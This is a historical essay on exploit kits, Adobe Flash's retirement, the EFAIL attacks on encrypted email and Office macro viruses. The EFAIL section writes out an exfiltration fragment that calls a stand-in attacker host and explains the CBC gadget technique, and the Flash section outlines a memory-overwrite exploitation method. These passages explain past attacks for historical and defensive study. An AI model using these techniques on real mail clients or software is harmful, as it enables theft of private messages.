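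### Which plugins the kits attacked

Flash and Java suited the kits because they were on most computers and their flaws worked much the same way in every browser. *Economic Factors of Vulnerability Trade and Exploitation* (2017), a study of underground sales, counted 18 Flash vulnerabilities and 15 Java ones among those that criminals traded. Attacks on Microsoft products sold more often on their own, outside kits. The balance between the two plugins later shifted towards Flash. Newly published attacks on Oracle's products, which included Java, fell sharply after 2013. Trend Micro's *Exploits as a Service* (2016), a security vendor's summary, named Flash as the software that kits attacked most and put it on more than a billion systems. For example, of four flaws that kits were using in 2016, three were in Flash, one was in Microsoft's Silverlight plugin and none was in Java.

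Kit developers rarely invented their own exploits. Trail of Bits, a security company, examined 18 exploits from the twenty leading kits and traced the crucial code in every one to researchers' publications, security firms' blog posts or attacks built for espionage, according to Dark Reading's *Attackers Crib Exploit Code, But Net Benefit For Defenders* (2013). Software makers had often issued a patch by the time a researcher published a method, so the kits depended heavily on people who had not installed the patch.

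It is harder to establish how many people ran outdated plugins. Blackhole's success rate gives an indirect answer, because an attack normally worked only on an unpatched computer. If 9 to 14 per cent of visitors were infected, at least that share had a vulnerable browser or plugin. The true share was probably higher, since antivirus software and crashes also stopped attacks. But the rate came from customers' screenshots, and a customer who bought poor traffic would have had a different result.

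### Blackhole

Blackhole's author was Dmitry Fedotov, a Russian who called himself Paunch. The Russian security firm Group-IB estimated that he had more than 1,000 customers and earned $50,000 a month. Most customers used the kit to spread Zeus and Citadel, programs that steal banking details. Krebs therefore considered the Russian interior ministry's figure of about $2.3 million for the gang's income a poor measure of the damage.

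In January 2013, the month Oracle released an emergency Java patch, a broker working with Fedotov offered $100,000 for undisclosed flaws, and he soon doubled the budget. Russian police arrested Fedotov that October. Shortly afterwards the broker, whose nickname was "J.P. Morgan", announced a $450,000 budget for a new kit of his own. A Moscow court sentenced Fedotov to seven years in April 2016.

The arrest ended Blackhole, but the kit was already declining. The security company Sophos had reported on its Naked Security blog in October 2013 that Blackhole accounted for only a small percentage of new infections. Other kits had copied its methods, and competition among them produced Angler.

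### Angler

Angler brought in much more money, mainly because many of its customers installed ransomware, which locks a victim's files and demands payment. An attacker could profit from any computer whose owner wanted the files back, even if it held no banking details. Biasini, a researcher in Cisco's Talos group, put the customers' ransomware income at about $60 million a year. The Record reported that Britain's National Crime Agency estimated Angler's yearly turnover at about $34 million and its peak share of all infections from kits at 40 per cent. The two sums may count different things, and neither comes from the criminals' own accounts.

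In June 2016 the Russian authorities arrested a group accused of stealing about $45 million from Russian banks with a program called Lurk. Within a week Angler had disappeared. Biasini found that one email account had registered about 85 per cent of the 125 or more domains used to control Lurk, and that the same account owned domains used by Angler. Kaspersky, the Russian security firm that had assisted in the arrests, concluded in *Angler by Lurk* (2016) that the gang had developed Angler and rented it out.

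American prosecutors later charged Maksim Silnikau and two others. The U.S. Department of Justice's *Leader of International Malvertising and Ransomware Schemes Extradited from Poland* alleges that they took a leading role in spreading Angler through advertisements, posing as legitimate advertising companies. Both accounts could be true if one group wrote the kit and another distributed it. Prosecutors also list "J.P. Morgan" among Silnikau's nicknames and date the scheme from October 2013, the month Fedotov's broker advertised for a new kit. The shared nickname doesn't prove that Silnikau was the broker. The Hacker News' *Ransom Cartel Creator Gets 16 Years in Prison for Operating Ransomware-as-a-Service* (2026) reports that a judge in Virginia sentenced Silnikau in August 2026 to 16 years for a separate ransomware business, and that the Angler case in New Jersey was still unresolved.

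### What the market needed

A permanent flaw does most harm when one attack works unchanged on many machines and each success earns money. Blue boxes met the first condition, since the same tone worked on trunks across the country, but most users gained only free calls. Exploit kits met both conditions. Kit developers needed a widespread target, a steady supply of fresh flaws, cheap visitors and a way to profit from victims they knew nothing about. They also needed the attack to run without the victim's help, since a prompt would have lost them some victims. Finally, they needed a way for specialists to find and pay one another, which criminal forums provided.

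These needs help in judging the explanations for the decline of exploit kits after 2016. Arrests removed suppliers, and they account well for the timing of Angler's disappearance. But Fedotov's earlier arrest had not stopped the trade, and in 2016 customers soon moved to two rivals, Rig and Neutrino, which raised their prices. Security Affairs reported that traffic to the other kits had fallen by about 96 per cent since early April, two months before the Lurk arrests. Biasini expected another kit to fill the gap, as Angler had after Blackhole. No kit became as dominant as Angler had been, and arrests alone don't explain why.

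Click-to-play and stricter defaults are better supported by the evidence, because they reached Java before Flash. *Economic Factors of Vulnerability Trade and Exploitation* notes that the fall in attacks on Oracle's products coincided with browsers blocking plugins and with Java's stricter default of January 2013. Kit authors went on attacking Flash, which was still running in most browsers. Arrests would have affected both plugins alike. The comparison can't separate the effect of the browsers' change from that of Oracle's, and it is based on published attacks, not infections, but it suggests that restricting a plugin drove attackers away from it, at first towards another plugin.

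Automatic updates probably mattered too, since the kits relied heavily on published flaws that people had not patched. Browser sandboxing made attacks harder, because an attacker who took over a confined plugin needed a second flaw to reach the rest of the computer. A failed attack seldom shows which defence stopped it, so it is hard to say how much either contributed. The declining use of plugins also reduced the number of targets, whether or not they were patched. The arrests explain why the market collapsed so suddenly, and these changes together probably explain why it did not recover.

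Much of the business survived without the plugins. Necurs, a network of infected computers that distributed ransomware and banking malware, went quiet at about the same time as Angler and returned after three weeks. The scheme in the New Jersey indictment continued until 2022 and included advertisements with false virus warnings, meant to get people to buy or install harmful software. Silnikau's ransomware business, which began in 2021, kept the kits' division of labour. He supplied the locking software, affiliates carried out most of the attacks, and brokers sold him stolen passwords for company networks.

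## Adobe Flash and its agreed end, 2010 to 2021

After browsers restricted Java, exploit kit developers concentrated on Flash, which most browsers still ran. Flash played animations, video and games inside web pages, and Adobe, its owner from 2005, distributed the player as a free plugin. In 2017 Adobe and five other companies agreed to retire it at the end of 2020. Adobe's stated reason was that open web standards such as HTML5 had matured enough to replace Flash, though people often attribute its end to insecurity.

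### What Flash did for the web

Flash dates from January 1996, according to Gadgets 360. Browsers at the time could display text and pictures but needed extra software to play a film or run a game. Designers used Flash to produce a single file in SWF format, which held the images, sounds, text and a compiled program written in the ActionScript language. The file looked the same in every browser that had the Flash player.

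Businesses came to depend on Flash. *Flash in the Dark* (Sridhar, Chirva and colleagues, 2017) reported that 24 of the 25 most popular Facebook games used it and that the top nine Flash games in China together earned more than $70 million a month. *Looking Back on Three Years of Flash-based Malware* (Wressnegger and Rieck, 2017) reported that about a quarter of the 1,000 most visited web pages still relied on Flash for video, games or advertisements in 2016.

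### Why the player kept producing memory errors

Flash Player was a large native-code program that opened files from untrusted sources. An SWF file consisted of containers called tags, of several dozen types, some nested inside others. The player needed code to interpret each type and handle whatever values the file supplied. In one flaw from 2007, a file gave a negative number for its count of scenes, which caused an arithmetic error that an attacker could exploit to run their own code without any ActionScript.

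ActionScript made other attacks easier because the attacker's program could arrange the player's memory before triggering a bug. Adobe also kept the engine for old versions of ActionScript so that old files would still play. Wressnegger and Rieck describe this engine as obsolete for more than ten years, but attackers long used files written for the new engine to load attacks on the old one.

Most of Flash's flaws were errors in handling memory, whereas most of Java's sandbox escapes abused trusted library code. Among the flaws Adobe fixed in one August 2015 update, The Register (2015) counted 15 cases of use-after-free, in which a program keeps using memory it has given up. Another five were type confusion, in which a program treats one kind of data as another, and most of the rest were buffer overflows or other memory corruption.

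Sridhar and colleagues classified the Flash records in MITRE's database of CVE numbers.

| Year | Flash vulnerabilities | Of these, memory errors |
|---|---|---|
| 2008 | 18 | 3 |
| 2009 | 21 | 10 |
| 2010 | 59 | 35 |
| 2011 | 63 | 48 |
| 2012 | 66 | 57 |
| 2013 | 56 | 53 |
| 2014 | 64 | 37 |
| 2015 | 328 | 264 |

The totals vary by source. ZATAZ (2012) counted 68 flaws in Adobe's bulletins for 2012, and HotHardware's *Adobe Flash Finished 2015 With Over 300 Exploits Discovered* gave 316 for 2015. Even within *Flash in the Dark*, the yearly figures, including 22 for early 2016, add up to 697, but the text gives a total of 711.

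A greater problem is that these figures, like MITRE's ranking, also reflect how hard researchers looked. Sridhar and colleagues attribute the fivefold jump between 2014 and 2015 partly to closer scrutiny, including the work of Project Zero, a Google team that searches for flaws in widely used software. In July 2015 Adobe credited that team with 20 flaws in a single bulletin, according to eWeek. Researchers who examine one component may also find several flaws in it at once. CVE Details' *Adobe » Flash Player* lists four records from one day in December 2016 for overflows in the code that searches text.

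Memory errors made up more than half of the Flash vulnerabilities recorded each year from 2010 on. However, *Despite Decline in Use of Adobe Flash, Vulnerabilities Will Continue*, Schoenfield's analysis for the security firm McAfee, suggests that researchers moved on to memory errors in 2015 after running out of easier flaws, such as those that let attackers insert scripts into web pages. This may be true of the researchers McAfee had in mind.

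Wressnegger and Rieck counted 595 flaws in Flash for 2015 and 2016 together, so 2016 had nearly as many as 2015. In 2017 the number fell to 70 by McAfee's count, or 63 according to the security firm Recorded Future.

### Sandboxes and automatic updates

From late 2010, Google and Adobe ran the Flash player in Chrome inside a sandbox, and Adobe later did the same for Firefox on Windows. The sandbox made attacks harder, but exploit kits were still using Flash flaws in 2016. It did not protect people who opened Flash files outside the browser. In June 2018, Krebs on Security reported that attackers were targeting people and companies in Doha, Qatar, with Office documents that exploited a new flaw in Flash.

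Automatic updates shortened the time attackers had to use a published flaw. According to Recorded Future, Adobe's statistics showed that hundreds of millions of users, out of billions, installed a new version within six weeks. But Recorded Future also cites research that attackers exploit a new flaw within two weeks on average, if they exploit it at all. Chrome and newer versions of Windows shortened the delay further by delivering Flash updates along with the browser's own. Automatic updates did not help companies that kept an old version for compatibility, or protect anyone from flaws Adobe didn't know about.

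Antivirus software also missed some new attacks. Wressnegger and Rieck collected 2.3 million Flash files submitted to a scanning service between December 2013 and January 2017. They found 814 that none of the service's virus scanners flagged at first but at least ten flagged later. They deliberately looked for such files, so the count doesn't measure how often scanners missed new attacks.

### The Hacking Team leak

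In July 2015 an intruder published internal files from Hacking Team, an Italian company that sold surveillance software to governments. The files included working attacks on three Flash flaws unknown to Adobe (zero-days). The leak made these attacks available to criminals, and at least one soon appeared in the Angler exploit kit.

In response, Mozilla made Firefox block Flash by default until Adobe fixed the flaws, as The Eclectic Light Company's *Adobe Flash Player 18.0.0.209* (2015) reported. Adobe released version 18.0.0.209 on 14 July. Graham Cluley's *Adobe patches Flash against zero-day vulnerabilities* praised Adobe for its speed.

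The same update contained defences that Google and Adobe had been developing. Brand and Evans (2015), two engineers at Project Zero, explained that the vast majority of recent Flash attacks, including at least two from the leak, used the same method:

1. The attacker found a bug that let a Flash file overwrite a small part of the player's memory.
2. The file's program created lists of numbers, arranged so that one of them lay where the bug would do its damage. Flash stored the length of each list at its beginning.
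3. The bug replaced that length with a much larger number.
4. The program could then read and write far beyond the end of the list, which gave the attacker a way to take over the player.

Google's defence moved the lists into a separate region of memory, so a bug in the main region could no longer reach them. Adobe's defence stored a secret check value with each length. An attacker who changed the length could not supply the matching value, so the player shut down. This check complemented the separation, which worked poorly in 32-bit versions because they had too little memory space to keep the regions far apart. The update also made the location of Flash's memory harder to predict.

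These measures were only mitigations. A month later Evans (2015) described three ways around Adobe's length check, which had by then been strengthened. In early 2018 attackers got past a similar check on another type of data. Schoenfield quotes a colleague at McAfee who nevertheless credits Adobe's measures with a recent decline in attacks on Flash. The number of new flaws with a severity score of 9 or more out of 10 also fell, from 294 in 2015 to 60 in 2017. Hardening probably contributed to both declines, but over the same period the large exploit kits disappeared and fewer sites used Flash.

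In 2018 the Rig exploit kit still offered 13 old attacks on Flash, at least two of which came from Hacking Team's leaked files.

### Apple's refusal

Apple released the iPhone in 2007 without support for Flash and never added it. On 29 April 2010 Steve Jobs, then Apple's chief executive, published an open letter explaining why. OS X Daily's *Steve Jobs posts his thoughts on Flash* (2010) lists six grounds:

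- Flash was a closed system under Adobe's control.
- People did not need it for video or for the rest of the web.
- It was unreliable, insecure and slow on mobile devices.
- It drained batteries.
- Its designers had made it for mice, not for touch screens.
- Apple did not want developers to depend on another company's tools.

Security was only part of one of these points, but it may have counted for more inside Apple. According to Cult of Mac, former Apple manager Bob Burrough said that the company had explored putting Flash on the iPhone but that Jobs did not trust Adobe to deal with its security problems. Adobe's chief executive replied to Jobs that Apple's own software caused the crashes, and denied that Flash was bad for batteries.

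Apple also had a commercial interest, since Flash would have let people play games on web pages without going through Apple's App Store. Two months before the letter, Elmer-DeWitt (2010) questioned Jobs's motives in *Why Is Steve Jobs Flash-obsessed?* but thought him at least partly sincere.

Pages that needed Flash did not work on an iPhone or iPad, so website owners had the same commercial reason to replace Flash as they had to replace ActiveX. Adobe made a Flash player for Android phones but released its last version in September 2013.

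### Open standards and browser restrictions

Flash's replacement was HTML5, a new version of the language web pages are written in, which let browsers play video without a plugin. Two related standards, WebGL for three-dimensional graphics and WebAssembly for running compiled programs at high speed, covered much of the rest of what Flash did. Schoenfield cites W3Techs surveys in which the share of websites using Flash fell steadily from 2011, reaching 5 per cent by early 2018.

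Browser makers reduced access to Flash in stages. In 2016, Chrome began to require a click before running it on certain sites, according to IT World Canada. In July 2017, Microsoft planned for Edge to request permission the first time a user visited most sites that needed Flash, and to save the answer until a later stage.

### The agreement of 25 July 2017

Adobe announced on 25 July 2017 that it would stop updating and distributing Flash Player at the end of 2020 (*Adobe bidding Flash farewell in 2020*, 2017). It had planned this with Apple, Facebook, Google, Microsoft and Mozilla. Adobe explained in *Flash & the Future of Interactive Content* that HTML5, WebGL and WebAssembly had matured into a "viable alternative" and that most browser makers were already building plugin functions into their browsers.

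A common date helped because no browser maker wanted to drop Flash alone. If only one had, people who needed Flash for a game or a training course could have switched to another browser, and website owners could have told them to. Once all the main browsers had the same deadline, owners had to replace their Flash content or lose it.

Adobe said it gave more than three years' notice because whole businesses in gaming, education and video depended on Flash. It promised security patches throughout, but planned to end Flash sooner in some countries where people were distributing outdated and unlicensed copies. The long notice also meant that users kept running the player while researchers and attackers found new flaws in it. In September 2019 the US National Security Agency was still warning organisations about the danger in *Continued Use of Adobe Flash Invites Compromise*.

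Apple's Safari 14 stopped loading Flash in September 2020. Adobe issued its last general update on 8 December and ended support on 31 December. On 12 January 2021 a block that Adobe had built into the player stopped it from playing Flash content. Adobe said the block was meant to help secure users' systems, and it urged users to uninstall the player.

Software makers rarely disable copies that people have already installed. Microsoft had used kill bits to do this, but only for individual ActiveX controls. Flash players too old to contain Adobe's block could have kept working, but the main browsers no longer loaded Flash. Adobe's licensees still supplied versions for China and for business customers.

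### Did insecurity kill Flash?

One explanation for Flash's end is that attacks made it too dangerous to keep. Kaspersky's *Gone in a Flash* (2021) says that many security experts had been advising people to abandon it for more than a decade. Adobe's 2017 announcement did not mention attacks, and mentioned security only in promising to maintain it until the end. Neither company was neutral. Kaspersky sells protection against attacks, and Adobe had little reason to dwell on the flaws of a product it was withdrawing, so its silence about attacks is weak evidence that security did not matter.

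Flash's early decline probably owed more to phones and HTML5 than to security. The share of websites using Flash was already falling in 2011, four years before the surge in reported flaws and the Hacking Team leak. Flash was dangerous by then too, and attackers used it that year to break into the security company RSA. But its flaws harmed RSA and visitors to hacked pages, while website owners lost customers if their pages did not work on phones.

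The Google Earth and Unity plugins, which displayed maps and games, are a rough comparison for Flash. They were not among the main targets of exploit kits, but Chrome's users abandoned them faster than they abandoned Java in 2013 and 2014, and Google removed the interface that all three used. A plugin without Flash's record of attacks would probably have disappeared from browsers too.

The effect of Apple's refusal to support Flash is hard to separate from that of open standards, because the refusal increased demand for HTML5, which in turn made the refusal easier to maintain. Adobe's withdrawal of Flash from Android suggests that it would have struggled on phones even without Apple's ban. But Android was not an independent test, because by then many website owners had already built iPhone versions of their pages that also worked on Android.

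In 2015, when many popular pages still needed Flash, Google kept it despite its insecurity and helped Adobe harden the player. Browsers also had memory errors, and Brand and Evans noted that several browsers already used the kind of separation that Google added to Flash. Browser makers kept fixing these errors because browsers had no substitute.

Security helps explain why Flash ended on a fixed date instead of fading away. If Flash had been outdated but safe, browser makers could have left it available to the few people who still needed it. But an unsupported Flash would have accumulated unpatched flaws, which gave Adobe a reason to disable copies already on people's computers. The six companies had an alternative by 2017, so it is much less clear whether they would have agreed to a fixed end date if the web had still depended on Flash.

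## HTML email and the EFAIL attacks on encrypted mail, 2018

Browser makers could retire Flash because HTML5 had replaced it. Email also uses HTML, which has no comparable replacement there. In 2018, researchers published the EFAIL attacks, which showed that a mail program could leak an encrypted message just by displaying it as HTML. Mail programs still display HTML, but most now restrict what a message can fetch or send while it is open.

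### What HTML lets a sender do

Email began as plain text. HTML added fonts, tables, pictures and links, which gave senders some control over the reader's screen. A link can show a bank's address but lead to a criminal's site. CSS, the language used to style HTML, can hide part of a message or stretch an invisible button across all of it, so that a click anywhere on the message presses the button.

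Pictures also let senders get information back. An HTML message can contain a picture's address instead of the picture itself, and the mail program then requests the picture from that address. A sender who puts a different address in each copy learns which recipients opened the message and when. The request may also reveal the reader's mail software and IP address, which gives a rough location. Advertisers often use a single transparent pixel for this, since they only need the request.

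### Containment without a standard

The standard for HTML in email dates from 1997 and has not changed since 1999. According to Hanno Böck's 2018 blog post *Efail*, the standard warned that running code from a message without careful restrictions was exceedingly dangerous. It mentioned the privacy risk of remote content but made no recommendation about it. Nobody had specified which parts of HTML an email may use, so each maker of email software decided for itself.

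Makers of mail programs broadly agreed that messages should not run scripts, the small programs that make web pages interactive. This is hard to enforce because scripts can hide in unusual places, such as drawings and mathematical formulas, and web standards keep changing. The makers disagreed about whether to load remote pictures automatically. Poddebniak, Dresen and colleagues tested 48 mail programs for *Efail* (2018) and found that 13 loaded remote pictures without asking, three of which had no setting to prevent it.

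Email programs still differ in whether they load remote pictures by default. Thunderbird and the classic version of Outlook for Windows block them unless the reader allows them. Gmail has shown them automatically since 2013, but Google's servers fetch them, which hides the reader's IP address from the sender. Apple added a similar optional relay to its Mail program in 2021. These relays still request whatever address the sender wrote, and EFAIL put the secret text into that address.

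Some users refused HTML and campaigned for text-only mail. Böck, who almost never used HTML mail, thought plain text was the safest choice but conceded that developers would not abandon HTML. Each mail program has to display what other programs send, including newsletters and invoices. If one maker had dropped HTML, its users would have found much of their mail harder to read and could have switched to a rival. Six companies could set an end date for Flash, but no small group controls email, because anyone can choose a mail program and write to users of any other.

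### How a message could leak itself

OpenPGP and S/MIME are standards for end-to-end encryption of email, which lets only the sender and the recipients read a message. Companies and governments mostly use S/MIME. Human rights organisations have recommended PGP, the program OpenPGP is based on, to people at high risk, such as journalists.

An EFAIL attacker must already have a copy of the encrypted message, perhaps from a hacked mail server. This is a demanding condition, but encryption is meant to protect people in that situation. The attacker cannot read the message but can send it to someone who can, either a recipient or the original sender, whose mail program can normally still decrypt it. The message may be years old.

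The simpler attack, direct exfiltration, needs no knowledge of cryptography:

1. The attacker writes an email in three parts. The first part starts the address of a remote picture but leaves its quotation mark open: `<img src="http://attacker.example/`
2. The second part is the stolen message, still encrypted and unchanged.
3. The third part closes the quotation mark and the picture tag: `">`
4. When the victim opens the email, the mail program decrypts the second part and joins all three into a single page.
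5. The decrypted text is now part of the picture's address. The program requests that address, and the attacker reads the message in the server's log.

Stronger encryption would not prevent this, because the mail program decrypts the message correctly before mixing it with the attacker's text. The mistake resembles the one behind SQL injection.

The other attack alters the encrypted message. S/MIME used a method called CBC, which encrypts text in blocks, of 16 bytes each with the common AES cipher. To recover a block, the mail program decrypts it with the key and then combines the result with the previous encrypted block:

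Pᵢ = D(Cᵢ) ⊕ Cᵢ₋₁

Here P is the readable text, C the encrypted text and D the decryption step. The symbol ⊕ is XOR, a bitwise operation in which combining a value with itself cancels it out. An attacker who knows the readable block Pᵢ can replace Cᵢ₋₁ with Cᵢ₋₁ ⊕ Pᵢ ⊕ P′, where P′ is any text the attacker chooses. When the program decrypts Cᵢ, everything cancels except P′, so the attacker can insert text into an encrypted message without the key.

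The attacker can easily learn one block, because encrypted S/MIME messages that also carry a signature typically start with "Content-type: multipart/signed". Each replaced block turns into random characters, but the attacker can place these inside an HTML attribute that mail programs ignore. By repeating the replacement, the attacker writes a picture tag in front of the secret text, which again becomes part of the picture's address. The researchers called the altered pairs of blocks malleability gadgets.

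S/MIME had no integrity check to reveal that a message had been changed. Digital signatures did not help, because an attacker could remove the signature and mail programs usually displayed messages with invalid signatures anyway. OpenPGP had a check, the modification detection code, which stores an encrypted fingerprint of the message. Attackers could remove it or relabel the message as an older type that had no check. A researcher had described the relabelling in 2002. Against OpenPGP, the attack succeeded only if the victim's software displayed the message despite the missing or failed check.

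OpenPGP also compresses text before encrypting it, so the attacker has to guess how the compressed message begins. Poddebniak and colleagues tested this on about 500,000 emails from the energy company Enron. The 500 most common beginnings covered about 41 per cent of them, and many mail programs accepted an email containing 500 separate guesses. They therefore expected one email to work against roughly 40 per cent of messages.

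### How many programs leaked

| What the researchers looked for | Programs tested | Programs affected |
|---|---|---|
| A way to leak S/MIME messages | 35 | 23 |
| A way to leak OpenPGP messages | 28 | 10 |
| HTML that got past the blocking of remote content | 48 | 22 |
| CSS that got past the blocking of remote content | 48 | 11 |
| Scripts that ran inside a message | 48 | 5 |

A draft of the paper marks ten of the 35 programs as not supporting S/MIME, so 23 of the 25 that did support it leaked. The two that did not leak, Claws and Mutt, are Linux programs built around plain text.

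Direct exfiltration worked against five programs. Apple's Mac and iPhone mail programs loaded remote pictures by default, so opening the email was enough. In others, including Thunderbird, the reader had to do something, such as click anywhere in the message. Thunderbird had contained the flaw since its first version in 2003.

The table also shows that blocking remote pictures protected readers less than the setting suggested. Three programs that blocked them in ordinary mail loaded them when the same message arrived encrypted. When checking an S/MIME signature, seven programs also requested missing certificates from a server that an attacker could control.

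### The argument over who was at fault

On 14 May 2018 the Electronic Frontier Foundation (EFF), a US digital-rights group, advised people to disable or uninstall the plugins that decrypted PGP mail automatically, and to use another service, such as the messaging app Signal, until the flaws were understood and fixed. They could still read old messages by decrypting them outside the mail program. EFF argued that the attack was simple and that PGP users had an unusually high need for protection. Updating one's own software was not enough, because an attacker could send the stolen message to a correspondent who had not updated.

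Koch (2018), in *Efail or OpenPGP is safer than S/MIME*, called the warning "pretty overblown". Werner Koch develops GnuPG, the free program that many OpenPGP plugins use for decryption. He blamed mail programs that joined decrypted HTML parts together and ignored GnuPG's error reports. He recommended using encryption with an integrity check and avoiding HTML mail or, failing that, blocking all access to external links. Hansen (2018) replied that OpenPGP's integrity check stopped the gadget attack "dead" if the mail program acted on the check's warning. SearchSecurity quoted another critic, Victors, who called the advice to disable plugins "excessive" because people would not use PGP without automatic decryption.

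Koch's argument holds for direct exfiltration, which happens entirely in the mail program. It is weaker for the gadget attack on OpenPGP, because the standard required software to treat a failed integrity check as a security problem but did not require it to withhold the decrypted text. A mail program could therefore show an altered message beside a warning and reasonably claim to follow the standard, although the text would already have been sent to the attacker by the time the reader saw the warning. GnuPG itself released the decrypted text before reporting the error, because it also handled files too large to hold in memory.

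Koch had a reason for not making every failure fatal. GnuPG also protects stored data, and he pointed out that someone might need to restore a two-year-old backup or read old love letters at a silver wedding. A strict rule that made old files unreadable would have harmed users too. But GnuPG could have used a different rule for email, refusing altered messages there while still offering a way to recover damaged files.

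Nobody could defend S/MIME this way, because it had no integrity check for mail programs to act on. Koch agreed that it had no short-term fix except giving up HTML mail. In June he still argued that EFAIL was only an HTML rendering bug. Hansen rejected that view because thousands of companies used S/MIME.

In an earlier post, Böck also blamed the encryption standards, and he was right to blame both them and HTML. Even with perfect encryption, a mail program could join a secret to an attacker's HTML, and removing HTML would not stop it from opening an altered attachment that sent its contents out. The attachment attack was harder to demonstrate. In December 2018 the slides for *Attacking end to end email encryption* still offered a crate of Club Mate, a caffeinated soft drink, to the first person who leaked a message through an attachment such as a PDF or Word file.

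### Patches, bypasses and new standards

Enigmail, Thunderbird's OpenPGP plugin, first tried to stop direct exfiltration by inserting quotation marks between the parts of a message, so that an attacker's unclosed address would end before the secret text. Like filtering quotation marks to prevent SQL injection, this failed against attacks that needed no quotation marks. Böck put the encrypted message in a text box inside a form, which would send the contents when the reader clicked. Thunderbird already disabled one kind of submit button but had missed another.

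Thunderbird fixed the button on 18 May, four days after EFAIL became public, but Böck then found that pressing Enter could also send a form. On 21 May Enigmail stopped decrypting messages that had other parts before the encrypted one. Böck responded by placing CSS after the encrypted part, which could add a sentence to the decrypted message asking the reader to forward it. Six days later Enigmail refused any message that mixed encrypted and unencrypted parts. This rule kept the attacker's text off the page, so Enigmail no longer had to detect each trick.

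The encryption standards changed more slowly. The revised S/MIME standard of 2019 recommended authenticated encryption, which combines encryption with an integrity check, and warned makers of mail programs to treat the parts of a message as if they came from different sources. OpenPGP's revision added a modern form of authenticated encryption in 2024. Neither revision changes messages an attacker already has, and mail programs that still accept the old formats must handle them safely. To protect against relabelling, the researchers had suggested deriving a different key for each encryption method, so that a message encrypted with the new method would not decrypt under the old one.

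Separating the parts is also difficult in companies where a central gateway decrypts incoming mail, because the employee's mail program receives ordinary text and cannot distinguish the parts that were encrypted. The researchers suggested that a gateway display only the first part and turn the rest into attachments.

Gillmor, Melnikov and Hoeneisen (2025), in *Guidance on End-to-End Email Security*, still used direct exfiltration as their example of how mail programs break encryption. They recommended that protection apply to a message as a whole. They also wrote that most programs with encryption did not yet follow their guidance. The guidance covers far more than EFAIL, so those programs are not necessarily still vulnerable to it.

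Mozilla (2026) fixed a related flaw in Thunderbird in January 2026. When a reader decrypted an OpenPGP message embedded in an HTML email, the sender's CSS still applied to the decrypted text. The sender could then combine style rules, fonts and animations to extract the text, but only if the reader had allowed remote content. As in EFAIL, the sender's HTML was not kept separate from the secret. Because Thunderbird blocks remote content by default, the text did not leak automatically. Mozilla rated the impact as moderate.

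### Closing the way out

EFAIL needed a secret on the reader's screen, an attacker's HTML that could reach it, and a request that carried the secret away. Mail programs have to display secrets, since people need to read their mail, and hostile HTML arrives in ordinary messages, but the programs can refuse to make the request. Poddebniak and colleagues wrote that reliably blocking every outgoing channel would have prevented all the attacks they presented. They still considered this a short-term measure, because it leaves the encryption flaw in place and an altered attachment might later send data out from another program.

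Makers of email programs could accept blocking remote content by default because most of an HTML message still works without it, including fonts, tables and links, and readers can choose to load the pictures. No similar compromise was possible with ActiveX, because any control that ran could do anything its user could do. AI assistants have since leaked data through the images and links in their own answers, and their makers have also blocked some of those requests.

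Finding every channel is difficult. Certificate checks, forms and obscure HTML elements all made requests that the setting for remote pictures did not cover. A list of forbidden requests therefore tends to miss some. A program that blocks all network access from a message, with a few exceptions, fails more safely. Böck recommended a similar approach for HTML itself, with a published list of the features email may use and everything else excluded.

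Blocking requests also doesn't stop a message from persuading its reader to do something harmful. Böck's last trick against Enigmail sent no data itself but displayed a false instruction above the decrypted text. A reader who obeyed it would have forwarded the secret to the attacker.

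## Office macros, 1995 to today

Microsoft Office documents can contain macros, which are small programs. From 2007, Office opened documents from strangers with macros switched off and showed a button to turn them on, so for years criminals wrote documents that tricked people into pressing it. In 2022, Microsoft removed the button for files that came from the internet.

### What a macro can do

Most macros automate repetitive office tasks. IT Brew's *After some block and forth, Microsoft stops Office macros by default* (2022) mentions unmerging all the merged cells in a spreadsheet and saving a workbook with the time in its name. Since Office 97, the main macro language has been Visual Basic for Applications (VBA). Excel also kept an older kind, known as XL4 or XLM macros.

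A macro can run without the user starting it. *In the Beginning was the Word* (Krukov, 1996) explained how this worked in the Word and Excel of the time. Word ran a macro named `AutoOpen` whenever someone opened the document that contained it. If a macro had the same name as one of Word's own commands, such as `FileSave`, Word ran the macro instead of the command. Macros could also call Windows functions, which gave them access to the rest of the computer.

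Honest developers use the same powers. A company can use `AutoOpen` to set up the menus that a form needs. *At last! Office macros from the internet to be blocked by default* (Ducklin, 2022) gives the example of a macro that takes over a menu command so that nobody prints a confidential document by mistake. A finance department's macro might fetch exchange rates from a server and save a report to disk. The macro in the clerk's invoice used the same operations to download and save malware.

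Office could detect that a document contained a macro but could not determine whether the macro was dangerous, as O'Reilly's *Office 2000 Security* points out. In *Office macro security* (2022), the Sophos writer Paul Ducklin compares a macro to an ordinary program file. A macro can do almost anything a program file can, but few people would accept a program by email, while most open documents without hesitation.

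### Concept and Melissa

The first widespread macro virus, Concept, appeared in 1995. The Christian Science Monitor's *New Kind of Virus Riles Fanfare for Windows 95* reported that viruses had until then spread only through files containing programs, so people had been able to treat documents as safe. Microsoft accidentally spread Concept on a CD-ROM it sent to hardware makers for testing Windows 95. According to Trend Micro's *20 Years of Macro Malware*, the virus only showed a box containing the number 1. *That didn't last! Microsoft turns off the Office security* (Ducklin, 2022) recalls that Microsoft called it a "prank macro".

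Concept used Word's global template, the file on which Word bases new documents. When someone opened an infected document, its macros copied themselves into the template, from which they could spread to other documents. The virus worked on any operating system with a suitable version of Word, and it spread easily because people exchanged documents far more often than programs. CERT Coordination Center (1999) cited a US government count of more than 1,000 macro virus variants by 1998.

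Microsoft included an option in Word 97 called "Macro virus protection", which alerted users when a document contained macros and offered to disable them. The alert was the same whether the macros were harmless or malicious.

Melissa showed that warnings did little to protect people who trusted the sender. It began to spread on Friday 26 March 1999 in emails from people the recipients knew, each with a Word document attached and the message "Here is that document you asked for". If the recipient opened the document and allowed macros, Melissa lowered Word's security setting so that no warning would appear again. It then used Microsoft Outlook to send itself to the first 50 entries in every address book it could read. It also infected Word's global template, after which it could attach the user's own documents to its emails and might leak confidential material.

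By Monday, Melissa had reached more than 100,000 computers, and one site had received 32,000 copies in 45 minutes. HSToday's *An $80 Million Cyber Crime in 1999 Foreshadowed Modern Threats* adds that it disrupted about a million email accounts. Yet CERT Coordination Center's *CERT Advisory CA-99-04* (1999) reported that Melissa was not known to exploit any new vulnerability. It used features of Word and Outlook that worked as Microsoft had designed them.

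### Signatures, and the return of the choice

Word 2000 introduced three security levels, and Microsoft (1999) told worried customers that the default, High, would protect them from Melissa. On High, Word disabled unsigned macros without telling the user. The user could run a macro signed by an unknown author only by choosing to trust that author permanently, according to Microsoft's *Using Signed Office VBA Projects*. Medium let the user decide about unsigned macros too, and Low ran everything.

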